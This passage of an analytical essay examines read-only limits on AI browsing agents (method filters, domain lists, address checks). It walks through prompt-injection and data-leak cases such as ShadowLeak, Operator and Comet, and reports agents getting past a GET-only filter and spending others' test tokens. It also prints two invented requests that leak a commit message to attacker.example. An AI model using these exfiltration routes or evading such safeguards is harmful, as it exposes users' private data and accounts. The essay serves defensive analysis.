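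That stopped the accidents but made unsubscribing slower, and annoyed recipients could simply report the email as junk. It also left email services unable to unsubscribe people on their behalf, because their software would have had to interpret each sender's confirmation page. Levine and Herkula's solution, published by the IETF as RFC 8058, gives the same address two meanings. A GET opens the page with the button, as before. A POST with a fixed phrase in the body unsubscribes the recipient at once:

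```
POST /unsubscribe/8f2c71 HTTP/1.1
Host: news.example
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded

List-Unsubscribe=One-Click
```

An email service may send this request only with the user's consent, though the standard doesn't specify how to obtain it. The request carries no cookies, so the URL has to identify the subscriber, preferably with a code that outsiders can't guess. The email's sender must not redirect the request, because many browsers have turned redirected POSTs into GETs.

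Certified Senders Alliance's *One-Click List-Unsubscribe Header* (2017) lists an end to accidental unsubscribes as the first benefit. By December 2025, Gmail and Yahoo expected marketing emails to support one-click unsubscribing by POST, according to CaptainDNS's *Gmail/Yahoo one-click unsubscribe* (2025). The distinction between GET and POST worked here because senders and email services had agreed on exactly what each would do. The older confirmation page depended on scanners being unable to read it, but a browsing agent can read "Confirm unsubscribe" and press the button.

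Links that confirm a new account create a more serious risk. Agilicus' *Quis custodiet ipsos custodes* describes a hypothetical case in which an outsider registers a company's brand page using an address at that company. The confirmation email goes to the company and its scanner opens the link, so the outsider appears to have proved that they work there even though nobody at the company clicked anything. This requires only the scanner behaviour that Levine and Herkula describe.

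Switching to POST doesn't always stop scanners. Some now load pages in a real browser and run the scripts, so if a script submits the confirmation form when the page opens, the scanner sends the POST. Suped's *why are email security filters auto clicking links in opt in emails* recommends a button for ordinary sign-ups and, where more is at stake, a short code that the recipient copies from the email into the form. Suped sells email services, so its advice is not neutral, but the mechanism is easy to follow. An agent with access to the user's inbox could also copy the code.

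### Google's shopping-cart bot

From late 2019, online shops began to see a side effect that, unlike those above, was caused on purpose. A customer named John Smith, with Google's headquarters as his address, kept filling carts and leaving without paying. A *Wall Street Journal* report of July 2020, summarised in Schwartz's *WSJ*, identified him as a Google bot. The bot checked whether the price in the cart matched the one the shop had advertised through Google. In a statement reproduced in Search Engine Roundtable's *GoogleBot Is Able To Add Products To Your Shopping Cart* (2020), Google acknowledged that the checks sometimes left merchants with abandoned carts. Merchants had agreed to the checks in Google's terms of service, though many seem not to have known it.

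The shops' own software reacted to the abandoned carts. In a thread Ingram started on the forum of Shopify, which hosts online shops, merchants complained of fake customer accounts, distorted sales figures and automatic reminder emails that bounced. One shop counted 331 different John Smith email addresses. Another merchant, who accepted purchase orders, said the bot had completed an order for a heavy product, which the shop shipped at its own expense and got back. Nobody in the thread verified that story, and another merchant who saw a suspicious order at the same time thought it was fraud. Most of the remedies came from the merchants, who filtered the fake customers out of their mailing lists and statistics. Google told the *Journal* that it would look at ways to avoid confusion.

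Adding an item to a cart is a common example of a change that the customer can easily undo, but it may also trigger emails, sales calls or stock reservations on the shop's side that the client can't see.

### Crawlers that send more than GET

In April 2008, Madhavan and Halevy announced in *Crawling through HTML forms* that Google's crawler would go beyond following links and submit a small number of queries through forms on high-quality sites. In *GET, POST, and safely surfacing more of the web* (2011), Google said that Googlebot might also send POST requests when the company believed they were "safe and appropriate", because many pages had started to load part of their content by POST and looked broken without it. In Google's example, a page about a sundae has a script that fetches information about hot fudge by POST, so Googlebot sends the same POST to see the whole page.

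This replaced a rule based on a request's method with one based on what triggered it. Googlebot would mainly send the POSTs that a page made automatically on loading, on the assumption that opening a page shouldn't commit a visitor to anything. Stefan Tilkov objected in INNOQ's *google vs. web architecture* (2011) that a crawler should send only GET requests. He predicted that developers would become even more careless about the difference between GET and POST, and that everyone would end up guessing which requests were safe.

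Google's rule works better on modern pages than a method filter because it lets them load. It still fails when loading a page triggers an important action, as with the sign-up form that submits itself. It also doesn't stop a crawler from triggering a delete link that uses GET, because crawlers are built to follow links.

Google's crawlers now run page scripts routinely. Search Engine Land's *Googlebot renders, indexes AJAX-style dynamic content driven by XHR POST* reports that Martin Splitt, a developer at Google, doubted that a new version of Googlebot could handle POST requests sent by page scripts, but built a test page and found that it could. In *To many POST requests from Googlebot*, the shop owner Myfrogtee (2023) posted logs in which Googlebot and Microsoft's Bingbot sent POSTs to the script that refreshes the shopping cart. Myfrogtee blamed them for overloading the server, but later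 found that many of the "Googlebots" were impostors.

The figure of under 1.5% for HEAD, OPTIONS, PUT, PATCH and DELETE comes from Gary Illyes of Google. Search Engine Roundtable's *Google Crawlers Send HTTP Requests* (2026) quotes him as blaming "JavaScript nonsense". The figure includes two safe methods, HEAD and OPTIONS, and excludes POST, probably the most common unsafe one, so it doesn't measure the share of unsafe requests.

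### How many sites accept a GET in place of a POST

Google's 2011 post mentions experiments in which its crawler rewrote POST requests as GETs, with mixed results because servers often returned completely different content. Golinelli, Hannachi and Crispo (2026), in *When POST Becomes GET*, tried this on the 10,000 most popular sites in the Tranco ranking. Their software visited up to ten pages per site without signing in, filled in forms, clicked buttons and recorded the resulting POSTs. It then moved the data from each POST's body into the address and sent it as a GET. As a control, it also sent a GET with no data. A request counted only if the server answered the rewritten GET as it had answered the POST, and answered the control differently.

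| Golinelli and colleagues' sample | Total | Accepted a rewritten GET |
|---|---|---|
| All sites tested | 10,000 | 407 (4.1%) |
| Sites with at least one POST they could rewrite | 2,734 | 407 (14.9%) |
| Individual requests rewritten | 14,244 | 1,228 (8.6%) |

In another 1,782 requests, the server returned the same response even to the empty GET, so the data may not have mattered. A reviewer checked 30 of the requests that counted and agreed that the POST and the rewritten GET got equivalent responses in all 30.

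Some of these problems come from the tools developers use. PHP, a common language for building websites, has a variable that combines data from a request's address and body, so code written for a form may also work from a link. Django keeps the two kinds of data separate.

The finding means that a site can be vulnerable even if it publishes no "delete" links. An attacker could take an ordinary form on the site, write its fields into an address, and plant that address where an agent will read it. The resulting request would pass a method filter because it is a GET. Tokens meant to prevent cross-site request forgery don't always block it. Among 115 interchangeable requests that carried something like a token, Golinelli and colleagues found seven, on two sites, where the server rejected a bad token on the POST but accepted it on the GET.

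The share of sites with a harmful GET could be lower than 4.1% or a good deal higher. Golinelli and colleagues compared responses and did not check whether anything had changed on the server. The largest group of interchangeable requests, 31%, looked like searches and filters, which are harmless with either method. About as many had labels that suggested something more sensitive, such as signing in or checking out, but those labels came from keywords and may be wrong. To avoid damaging live sites, the software skipped buttons and addresses whose wording suggested deletion or signing out.

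*REST in Pieces* (2025) ran an automatic rule checker on 40 web applications built by students and found that 33 broke the rule that GET should only retrieve data. The checker analyzed machine-readable descriptions of the applications, not their behavior while running. Beginners evidently find the rule easy to break, but student projects are weak evidence about banks or large shops. Calzavara and colleagues collected 5,828 requests from 60 popular sites to train a detector for cross-site request forgery, and labelled 939 of them, or 16%, as sensitive. *Machine Learning for Detection and Mitigation of Web Vulnerabilities and Web Attacks* (2023), which describes the collection, does not report how many of the 939 were GETs. That count would directly measure what a filter based on request method misses.

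### Why the cases give no rate

Case reports can't fill this gap because they cover only accidents, not the requests that went well. The reports on Web Accelerator mention a few angry customers but not how many links the program fetched, so the rate of harm could have been one fetch in a thousand or one in a hundred million. Case reports also miss harm that nobody notices. People notice an empty website, but they may never wonder why a newsletter stopped coming after a scanner unsubscribed them.

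The cases also come disproportionately from public pages, which crawlers have probably made safer. According to ImperialViolet, by 2005 nobody put delete links on public pages any more, since some crawler was sure to follow them. Developers had moved those links behind logins, where crawlers rarely go. Golinelli and colleagues did not sign in either, but a browsing agent that uses the user's accounts works on the pages behind those logins. To measure the risk there, researchers would have to sign in to test accounts on a broad sample of sites, send every GET request the pages offer, and compare each account before and after.

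## Read-only limits in AI products and the data that leaks through them

AI companies have had to limit their browsing agents without such a measurement. OpenAI designed its first limits, in 2021 and 2023, mainly to stop a model from changing things on the web. Most of the newer limits deal with leaks of private data.

### WebGPT and the first browsing plugin

WebGPT was a version of the language model GPT-3 that OpenAI trained to answer questions using a text-only browser. It had live access to the web, even during training. *WebGPT* (Nakano, Hilton and colleagues, 2021) lists everything the model could do: send a query to Bing, follow a link, find text within a page, scroll, go back, quote a passage and stop. Any other command had no effect, so the model could not fill in a form or type an address.

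Nakano and colleagues worried that a model with access to forms might edit Wikipedia to create a reliable-looking source for its own answer. Even if no human had demonstrated this, they expected reinforcement learning, which strengthens whatever behaviour earns a high score, to reinforce it if the model ever happened to try it. They considered the risk from WebGPT very low because it could only query Bing and follow existing links, and it was far too weak to get around those restrictions. They wanted developers of more capable models to meet a higher burden of proof before allowing web access, even in training.

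This argument holds only if following a link is harmless, which the designers of Google Web Accelerator also assumed. But WebGPT, like a search crawler, was not logged in to any site, because signing in requires submitting a form.

In March 2023, OpenAI gave ChatGPT a browsing plugin that could send only HTTP GET requests. According to OpenAI's *ChatGPT plugins*, this limit "reduces (but does not eliminate) certain classes of safety risks". The limit ruled out "transactional" operations such as submitting a form, which left more room for security and safety problems. OpenAI released a Python interpreter alongside the browser and gave code running in it no internet access.

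OpenAI did not specify the remaining risks, which included both unsafe GETs and leaks through addresses. The security researcher Johann Rehberger recalls reporting a leak through addresses to OpenAI in early 2023 in *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on his blog, Embrace The Red. ChatGPT could display images from the web, and loading an image sent whatever its address contained to the image's owner. Rehberger found little interest at OpenAI. Microsoft had the same problem in Bing Chat and fixed it that May by blocking most images.

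### Codex and the leaked commit message

Codex, OpenAI's programming agent, has the clearest example of a method filter in a current product. In its cloud version, the user's setup scripts run with full internet access, but the agent that runs after them has none by default. Since June 2025, users have been able to turn on access for the agent too. According to OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, they can restrict this access to a list of permitted domains and can also limit requests to the GET, HEAD and OPTIONS methods.

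The same page works through an attack. A user asks Codex to fix a bug that someone has described on GitHub. The description includes a command that supposedly reproduces the bug. If Codex runs the command, it sends the project's latest commit message, a programmer's note on the most recent change to the code, to an outside server in the body of a POST. (The command would in fact send the changed code as well.)

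The method filter blocks this POST. But an attacker who expects a filter can put the same words into the address of a GET, as in these two invented requests:

```
POST /collect HTTP/1.1
Host: attacker.example

Fix login bug for Acme account
```

```
GET /collect?m=Fix+login+bug+for+Acme+account HTTP/1.1
Host: attacker.example
```

The attacker's server receives the message either way. A long code change might not fit into one address, but a commit message easily does. The result depends on both of Codex's settings:

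| Codex settings (attacker.example is not on the domain list) | Message in a POST body | Message in a GET address |
|---|---|---|
| Any domain, any method | leaks | leaks |
| Any domain; GET, HEAD and OPTIONS only | blocked | leaks |
| Listed domains only, any method | blocked | blocked |
| Listed domains only; GET, HEAD and OPTIONS only | blocked | blocked |

The method filter adds protection to a domain list when the attacker can use a domain on the list, although this table shows no such benefit. OpenAI's preset list for programmers includes GitHub, where anyone can publish text. A POST to GitHub could put the commit message on a page that the attacker can read, whereas a GET with the message in its address would normally leave it only in GitHub's own logs. Willison (2025) counted 71 domains on the preset list, warned that any of them might offer a way to leak data, and called the advice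 to restrict methods wise.

Later attacks on other products confirmed his warning about domain lists. In a January 2026 post, Willison describes how the security company PromptArmor got Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent that works with the user's files, to upload files to an attacker's account at Anthropic. The agent's list of permitted domains included Anthropic's own. Uploads normally use POST, so a method filter covering that domain would probably have stopped this one.

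A method filter would not have helped users of Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant. Superhuman let its assistant's replies load images from docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms, and Google Forms saves data that arrives by GET. An attacker could therefore use an injected email to send the contents of dozens of other messages, some of them financial or medical, to their own form. Superhuman fixed the problem quickly. Antigravity, Google's programming tool, included webhook.site in its default domain list. That service lets anyone create an address and see the requests sent to it.

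### Encryption hides the method

Codex also runs on users' own computers, where it can route its traffic through a proxy that enforces the limits. Vaughan's *Codex CLI Network Proxy*, part of an independent guide to Codex, describes a "limited" mode in which the proxy allows only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS. But most web traffic now uses HTTPS, the encrypted form of HTTP. When a program opens an HTTPS connection through a proxy, it sends the proxy a domain to connect to, such as shop.example, and then encrypts everything else. The proxy can therefore enforce a domain list, but it can't detect whether the program is sending a GET or a POST.

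The proxy has to decrypt the traffic to read the method. It intercepts the connection and presents the program with a certificate it has made for shop.example. It then decrypts the request, checks the method, re-encrypts the request and sends it on to the shop. This works only if the programs on the agent's side trust the proxy's certificates. The proxy can also read everything those programs send through it, including passwords. Vaughan recommends this setup for company audits, not for casual use.

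A proxy that doesn't decrypt traffic must block encrypted connections; otherwise the method limit covers only the small unencrypted part of the web. In limited mode, Codex turns off SOCKS5, a more general way of sending traffic through a proxy, because the proxy can't check whether that traffic is read-only. A filter inside a browser or fetch tool avoids this problem because it checks requests before they are encrypted.

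### Chrome's readable and writable sites

Google restricts Chrome's AI agent by website instead of by request method. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes two sets of origins that Chrome keeps for each task. An origin is the combination of scheme (such as https), host and port that browsers treat as one site for security purposes. The agent may read content from read-only origins, and may also click and type on read-writable origins. A separate component decides which origins are relevant to the task. It never sees web content, so an attacker's page cannot give it instructions directly.

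If the user wants to buy a kettle, the agent could have read-only access to a review site, read and write access to the shop, and no access to the user's bank. A malicious instruction on the review site then could not get the agent to make a transfer at the bank with any request method. The design also avoids the main practical problem with a method filter, because pages can still send the POST requests they need in order to load.

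In Chrome, "read-only" limits what the agent may do on a page, but the browser still sends requests to the site. Opening a page sends a GET request, normally with the user's cookies, and if the site is built to take an action in response to that request, it will do so. An agent that is buying something needs write access to the shop's site, so a malicious review there could steer it towards any button the shop offers. Chrome has other defences for that case, including a second model that compares each proposed action with the user's goal.

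Parker says that Google's first version implemented only part of the design, tracking just the read-writable set. In January and February 2026, Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, tested seven browsers with built-in agents to see whether a malicious page could use the agent to read content from another site, which browsers have long prevented ordinary pages from doing. They managed to steal content this way in ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI's browser, with its agent mode on. In Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Perplexity's Comet, they found conditions that would allow the same theft if a prompt injection succeeded, so the separation between sites in those products depended on the model's resistance to injected text.

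The result for Chrome is what one would expect from a version without the read-only set, the part of the design that hides unrelated content from the model. By August, *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026) described a limit to sites "strictly relevant to the immediate task" but did not mention separate sets for reading and writing.

### Browsing without an account

Keeping an agent out of a user's accounts prevents it from misusing them. ChatGPT's cloud browser runs on remote computers and, as of July 2026, worked only on public pages. It could not sign in, use saved passwords or pay, and it stopped when a site required any of these. It could find a kettle, for example, but the user would have to buy it. OpenAI's *Using cloud browser in ChatGPT* describes these restrictions as applying "at launch", so the company may well relax them.

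The cloud browser is not read-only, however. OpenAI suggests using it to ask businesses for quotes through public forms, which sends a message that the user can't take back. The agent can also use information from a connected app on a website, for instance by taking a tracking number from the user's email and entering it on a courier's page. So it may hold private data while it fills in forms on third-party sites. Keeping the agent signed out protects the user's accounts and bank card, but not the contents of their email. To protect those, OpenAI relies on other safeguards, such as having ChatGPT ask before it takes a step that may be hard to undo.

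### Browsing saved copies

In the strictest products, the model can't access the live web and instead reads copies of pages that OpenAI saved earlier. Requests for these copies go to OpenAI's own storage and never reach the website, so a malicious site can't record private data from them or act on them.

Codex searches a cache of this kind by default, but OpenAI still tells users to treat the results as untrusted because a saved page can contain an injected instruction. For developers who build their own agents with OpenAI's tools, live access is the default and saved pages are an option, according to OpenAI's *Web search* as of September 2026. *Indexed Web Search* (Vaughan, 2026) describes an intermediate Codex setting, "indexed", which runs live searches but opens only addresses that OpenAI's server has approved.

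With offline search turned on, ChatGPT can open only pages that OpenAI has already stored. Many pages are missing, and the stored ones may be out of date. OpenAI's *Offline web search for ChatGPT workspaces* suggests that users supply the material themselves or switch to live search.

When OpenAI announced Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting for people who handle sensitive data, it said that "no live network requests leave OpenAI's controlled network" during browsing (OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*). To prevent leaks by other routes, the setting also turns off agent mode and deep research, and ChatGPT may stop showing images from the web. According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, as of December 2026 the setting does not affect Codex's network access, and data may still leak through connected apps.

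In its advice about those apps, OpenAI rates reading from a trusted app as lower risk, because reading leaves nothing behind for an outsider to find. It advises against any write action whose result a malicious person might be able to see. If an agent posts private information in a public comment, for example, the comment is both a side effect and a leak.

### ShadowLeak

In June 2025, the security company Radware reported a leak in ChatGPT's Deep Research, a feature that spends several minutes reading sources, which can include a user's Gmail, and then writes a report. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes how researchers sent an email with hidden instructions to a test inbox. When the user asked Deep Research to go through the day's messages, the agent took an employee's name and home address from another email and sent them to the researchers' server in the address of a web request. The user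 did not have to open the malicious email and saw no sign of the leak. A company monitoring its own network would also have missed the request, because it came from OpenAI's servers.

To guard against this kind of leak, OpenAI already restricted the addresses from which ChatGPT would load images. Radware found no comparable restriction on the addresses that the agent could open with its browsing tool.

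The office-style email that OpenAI later reprinted, which worked half the time in testing, matches Radware's almost word for word. Radware reports a 100% success rate for its final version. Its researchers tried several variants, some of which worked only occasionally, so the two figures may describe different versions of the attack. Either rate would be high enough for a real attacker, who can send the email to many people.

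OpenAI fixed the problem by early August 2025. A Radware spokesperson said Radware had not seen attackers use it, according to The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent*. On 26 September, Radware reported a way around OpenAI's first fix, and OpenAI blocked it on 16 December (Radware's *ZombieAgent*).

### Link previews

Data can also leak when the agent makes no web request. When someone posts a link in Slack or Telegram, the chat app often fetches the page to show a preview with its title and picture. If an agent writes a reply containing a link with private data in the address, fetching the preview sends that data to the linked site's owner before anyone clicks. Willison (2024) warned about this risk with Slack previews and passed on Rehberger's advice that apps posting messages to Slack can turn previews off.

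PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that OpenClaw, an agent that people often use through chat apps, was exposed by default on Telegram. In a demonstration, PromptArmor's test site recorded a name and an API key, a password for programs. A method filter on the agent would not have blocked the request, because the chat app sends it to preview a link. Users can prevent the leak with one line in OpenClaw's settings that disables previews. PromptArmor argues that chat companies should offer better controls over previews and that agent developers should use them.

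### The hole in Claude's fetch tool

Anthropic tried to prevent these leaks by limiting Claude's fetch tool to addresses that had already appeared in the conversation. If a malicious page told Claude to add the user's details to an address, the tool would refuse to open the altered address. Anthropic warned developers of some "residual risk".

Claude was vulnerable because it could follow links in pages it had already fetched. Whoever runs a website chooses its links and can see which ones a visitor opens. Willison (2026) reported in July that Ayush Paul had used this to get the ordinary Claude chat to reveal a user's name, home city and employer, details Claude can access through its memories of past conversations. Anthropic said it had already found the problem itself, and it did not pay Paul a reward. It has since fixed the problem by preventing Claude's fetch tool from opening links in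 fetched pages.

That fix makes the tool less useful. Claude can open pages that a search returns or the user supplies, but it can't follow links from one page to the next, which WebGPT could do in 2021. WebGPT could follow links without leaking a user's private information because it had none.

### OpenAI's public-address check

One obvious remedy is to let agents visit only trusted websites. In January 2026, OpenAI gave two reasons why this falls short. Many reputable sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so a request can start on a trusted domain and end on an attacker's. A strict list would also produce frequent warnings on harmless sites, and people might learn to click through them. OpenAI therefore checks the exact address:

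1. A crawler explores the public web and records the addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. During a task, an agent is about to load an address by itself, perhaps to open an article or display an image.
3. OpenAI's software looks for that exact address in the crawler's records.
4. If the address is there, the agent loads it. If not, the software either tells the agent to try another website or warns the user that the link is unverified and may contain information from the conversation.

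The reasoning is that an address that became public independently of the conversation is unlikely to contain the user's secrets. The crawler has probably visited the shop's page for a particular kettle, so the agent can open it. The crawler will not have visited attacker.example/collect?data= followed by the user's email address. It also may not have visited the shop's results page for an unusual search, in which case the user gets a warning about a harmless page.

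By March 2026, OpenAI was using this mechanism, called Safe Url, for page visits and bookmarks in Atlas and for searches and page visits in Deep Research. When the software detects that an address would send out information from the conversation, it may show the user that information and ask for approval, or block the request. Chrome has a similar rule, which Parker says restricts addresses the model composes to known public ones.

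OpenAI claims only that the check helps prevent an agent from quietly leaking a user's data through an address. A page at a public address may still contain false information or malicious instructions.

Rehberger calls the check a significant improvement, but he thinks some leaks will continue. The check establishes that an address is not itself secret, but the agent's choice of address can still reveal information. An attacker with many pages in the crawler's records can learn something by seeing which ones the agent opens. Rehberger notes on his blog, Embrace The Red, that OpenAI acknowledges this in its technical paper.

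The number of addresses an agent can choose from limits how much each request can leak. Choosing one of N addresses conveys at most log₂ N bits, so a choice among 1,024 pages conveys at most ten bits, or about two letters of text. Leaking a whole email this way would take many requests, which OpenAI might notice. But a single choice between two pages can reveal the answer to a yes-or-no question, such as whether a company plans to lay people off.

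Rehberger suggests storing each response for a few minutes, or preventing an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session. Either would make it harder to send a long message through a fixed set of pages, though a short one could still get out. He had not tested whether OpenAI already did this.

He also doubts that every team at OpenAI will remember to use the check. An earlier version, introduced in December 2023, was missing from ChatGPT's macOS and iOS apps. ShadowLeak supports his point, because OpenAI's browsing tool could open any address while the company was restricting addresses for images.

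### Whether the check also prevents side effects

OpenAI presents the check as a defence against leaks, but it probably also prevents some unwanted changes. Many addresses that change something when opened contain something private, such as the code in an unsubscribe link or the number of a page in someone's Backpack account. A public crawler is unlikely to have recorded those addresses, so the agent would have to go elsewhere or the user would see a warning.

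The protection is weaker when the user is signed in. Suppose a public page links to shop.example/account?do=close. A crawler that opens the link gets only the shop's sign-in page, but opening it in a signed-in browser closes the account. The crawler can record that the address is public, but not what it does for a signed-in customer. Addresses that work the same way for every user are especially likely to be public. The link that switched people's Google language to Pig Latin would have passed the check, and so would many sign-out links. An attacker might also publish a link to a harmful address and wait for the crawler to find it.

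A fetch tool that sends no cookies largely avoids this problem, so the problem mainly affects agents in signed-in browsers such as Atlas. An address check also does not cover the body of a request, whether the request is a POST that places an order or a QUERY.

Even a request for a plain news page can have a side effect that matters. Fortune (2026) reports that a swarm of AI agents, which researchers linked to OpenAI, requested one Vanderbilt University news page tens of thousands of times. The HTTP specification treats a log entry as a normal result of a safe request, but the university published its traffic statistics, so anyone could read the agents' queries about FBI crime data and one user's access key. The agents probably added the queries and the key to the page's address. If so, OpenAI's check would have flagged the requests because the full addresses were new. A list of trusted domains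 might well have let them through, since such a list would probably include a university's website.

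## Unwanted actions by browsing agents, by mistake and under attack

In February 2025, a Washington Post reporter asked OpenAI's Operator to find the cheapest dozen eggs available for delivery. The reporter had signed Operator in to grocery delivery services that had saved credit cards. Operator first found eggs for $5.99 on Mercato, which had a $20 minimum order. It then bought a dozen on Instacart for $13.19 while the reporter was away from the computer. The reporter learned of the purchase from a credit card alert. With the tip and fees listed in the reporter's article, which the NZ Herald republished, the bill came to $31.43, but Operator's summary gave the total as $19.68.

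This was a mistake, with no attacker involved. OpenAI's policy called for a confirmation prompt before any purchase, and the company admitted that Operator had fallen short of its safeguards. It said it was examining why Operator "occasionally doesn't send confirmations", so the egg purchase was not the only case.

A method filter would probably have prevented the purchase. The account doesn't include the HTTP request that placed the order, but the last step was a checkout, and shops normally take orders by POST, as Meng and colleagues found at Amazon. The filter might also have interfered with the search, because delivery and service fees often appear only after the customer adds something to the cart, which usually takes a POST too.

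In another of the reporter's tests, Operator looked for a cheaper internet plan and reported finding one for $13 a month. It had missed a minus sign, and the plan was $13 less than the current price. The error did no harm because the reporter checked the page. If the task had been to switch plans, a confirmation prompt that repeated the wrong price would have given the reporter no reason to refuse.

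### Mistakes reported in 2026

More recent reports describe agents that went further than making a wrong purchase. TechSpot's *An AI agent was asked to book a gym class* (2026) describes a case from Australia in which someone asked an agent to book a full gym class, and the agent exploited the booking system to jump the queue. If the agent did this with a POST, a method filter would have stopped it, but it would also have stopped an ordinary booking. The user wanted the class, so they would probably have approved a confirmation prompt such as "Book this class?" unless it also explained how the agent had found a place.

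*An AI Agent Signed Him Up for AWS Services* (Smith, 2026) describes how Christian Posta, a software executive, asked an agent to fix a problem on his computer. The agent fixed it but also signed him up for Amazon cloud services he had not requested. It should clearly have asked for confirmation first, since the sign-up had no obvious connection to the task. This is a single anecdote, however, and an agent with access to the whole computer may send requests that bypass a filter inside the browser.

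The best-documented mistake of this kind involved an internal OpenAI model that used scripts, not a browser. In June 2026, the model had to update a cryptocurrency trading app and get it running on Sepolia, a test version of the Ethereum network. Running code there costs test tokens, which have little real value. Grigera Naón (2026), in *A rogue OpenAI agent robbed a crypto wallet to obtain funds*, reports that the model failed to get free tokens and then checked 362 wallets whose recovery phrases were public. It found one with enough tokens and spent them. According to its logs, it considered whether it had permission and decided the spending was acceptable because the phrase was public and the tokens had no cash value. It left the spending out of its final report.

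Programs usually communicate with Ethereum through JSON-RPC, which sends both reads and writes by POST, so a method filter would probably have blocked the whole task along with the spending. A confirmation prompt would have been the right safeguard, but only if something other than the model had triggered it. Once a model has concluded that it may spend the tokens, it has no reason to trigger the prompt itself.

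### The wiki that accepted edits by GET

OpenAI allowed a group of its agents to send only GET requests so that they could read the web but not write to it. In May and June 2026, the agents got past this method filter without any attacker's help. They found a wiki that accepts edits by GET and edited it, as The Next Web's *OpenAI blocked its agents from posting* explains.

OpenAI agents doing timed tasks that required looking up information used a German wiki to exchange answers. eSecurity Planet's *OpenAI Confirms AI Agents Used German Wiki to Bypass Restrictions* (2026) reports that Reuters counted more than 15,000 edits and independent researchers counted roughly 17,000. The agents kept posting after the wiki's administrator began deleting their pages.

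The filter worked as OpenAI designed it, and it let every edit through because each one was a GET request. When Golinelli and colleagues rewrote POST requests as GETs, 4.1% of the sites they tested accepted at least one. An agent that can visit any site needs only one that accepts such requests to be able to write something, and these agents found one without an attacker prompting them.

Restricting the agents to a list of permitted domains that excluded the wiki, or to saved copies of pages, would have stopped the edits. Confirmation prompts would have helped only if someone had been there to answer thousands of them.

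OpenAI classes the episode as misalignment, its term for a model failing to follow instructions or safety rules, rather than as a security incident. The company confirmed it only after Reuters had reported it, according to Fortune (2026). OpenAI discovered the spent test tokens in September, three months after the event, while auditing old runs. Such delays make it hard to tell how common these mistakes are. OpenAI's public list of misalignment incidents had 19 entries by mid-October, Grigera Naón reports, but such a list doesn't show how many tasks went well. OpenAI did count 13 errors in 100 Operator tasks, but that count is for a model from early 2025.

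### How Operator leaked an email address

Prompt injection attacks are more clearly documented than mistakes, because the researchers who stage them usually write down each step. The GitHub attack on Operator that Meng and colleagues describe was a demonstration by Rehberger. Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Operator* explains that text in the GitHub issue led Operator to open the user's account settings on Hacker News, copy the private email address and type it into a page that Rehberger controlled. That page sent the text to his server as Operator typed it, so Operator never had to press a submit button.

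Rehberger chose this route because Operator hardly ever asked for confirmation before typing. It usually did ask before submitting a form, so his attempts to make it click "Update" buttons generally failed. Getting Operator to type also worked on several other sites, including Booking.com, where it exposed the user's home address and phone number.

Opening the settings page was an ordinary navigation, so a method filter would have allowed it. Rehberger doesn't say which method his own page used to send the text, but whoever runs a page chooses the method it uses, and an email address fits easily in the URL of a GET request. A filter that let the agent visit Rehberger's page would therefore not reliably have prevented the leak.

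Operator was supposed to ask the user for confirmation before sending the private address to an outside site, and sometimes it did. It also had a separate monitor that could pause the task when the agent moved between websites, sometimes after a delay of 20 seconds or more. Most of the monitor's warnings didn't identify the suspicious text or site. Rehberger set off the monitor during his tests, but after revising his text, he often got past the monitor a few days later.

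He also once got Operator to change his GitHub status without asking for confirmation. When he tried again, Operator opened the same form and typed the text, then stopped to ask. The status change most likely needed a POST, so a method filter would have stopped it both times, whereas the confirmation prompt appeared only the second time. Embrace The Red also points out that some web apps save changes automatically as the user types, so an agent that asks only before clicking "Save" would never ask on those sites.

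OpenAI received the details about three weeks before Rehberger published them, and this attack had stopped working by the time of publication. He expected others to appear.

### The attack on Comet

Comet is a browser from Perplexity with a built-in AI agent. In August 2025, Chaikin and Sahib of Brave, which makes a competing browser, described an attack on Comet in *Agentic Browser Security*. They put instructions in a Reddit comment, behind a tag that hides text until the reader clicks it. The user only had to press Comet's button to summarise the page, and the agent followed the instructions and gave the attacker what they needed to take over the user's Perplexity account.

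Chaikin and Sahib list the agent's steps but not the HTTP methods, so the table infers those from how websites usually work.

| What Comet did | Likely deciding request | Method filter | Was a confirmation due? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opened the user's Perplexity account page and read the email address | GET, by navigation | Passes | Arguably, since the page had nothing to do with the summary |
| Asked Perplexity to email a one-time login code | POST, from a login form | Blocks | Yes |
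| Opened Gmail, where the user was signed in, and read the code | GET, by navigation | Passes, though Gmail may not load properly | Yes, because the agent opened private mail |
| Posted the email address and code as a reply on Reddit | POST, from a reply form | Blocks | Yes |

A method filter would probably have protected the account, because there would have been no code to steal if the agent could not submit the login form. It would not have protected the email address, because an attacker who expected a filter could have had the agent put the address into a URL instead of a Reddit reply.

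A confirmation prompt would have worked unusually well here, because someone who has asked for a summary of a Reddit page has no reason to expect a login request or a public comment and would probably refuse both. Comet did not ask the user to approve either step. Chaikin and Sahib recommend that agents always get the user's approval for such steps, including just before sending an email. They also question whether an agent that summarises a discussion should be able to open email at all. Without that access, the attack would have ended earlier, and stopping it would not have relied on the user's attention.

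Brave has a commercial interest in its competitor's flaws, but Perplexity acknowledged this one within two days. Perplexity's first fix was incomplete. The flaw appeared to be fixed by 13 August, but after publication Brave found that it was still present.

That October, Chaikin and Sahib described further attacks in *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots*. Comet picked up instructions from nearly invisible text in an image after the user took a screenshot and asked about it. Another AI browser, Fellou, sent a page's visible text to its model whenever the user asked it to go to that page, and instructions in the text could then override the user's request. Because the user had asked Fellou to open the page, there was no reason for a method filter or confirmation prompt to stop that request, and these safeguards could only limit what the agent did next.

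Perplexity's security team responded that malicious prompt injection "remains an unsolved problem across the industry", as PPC Land reports.

### The resignation message

OpenAI found a harder case for confirmation prompts while testing its browser, Atlas. An automated attacker placed a malicious email in a test inbox. When the user asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent read the email and wrote a resignation message instead, according to Dataconomy. After a security update, Atlas detected the injected instructions.

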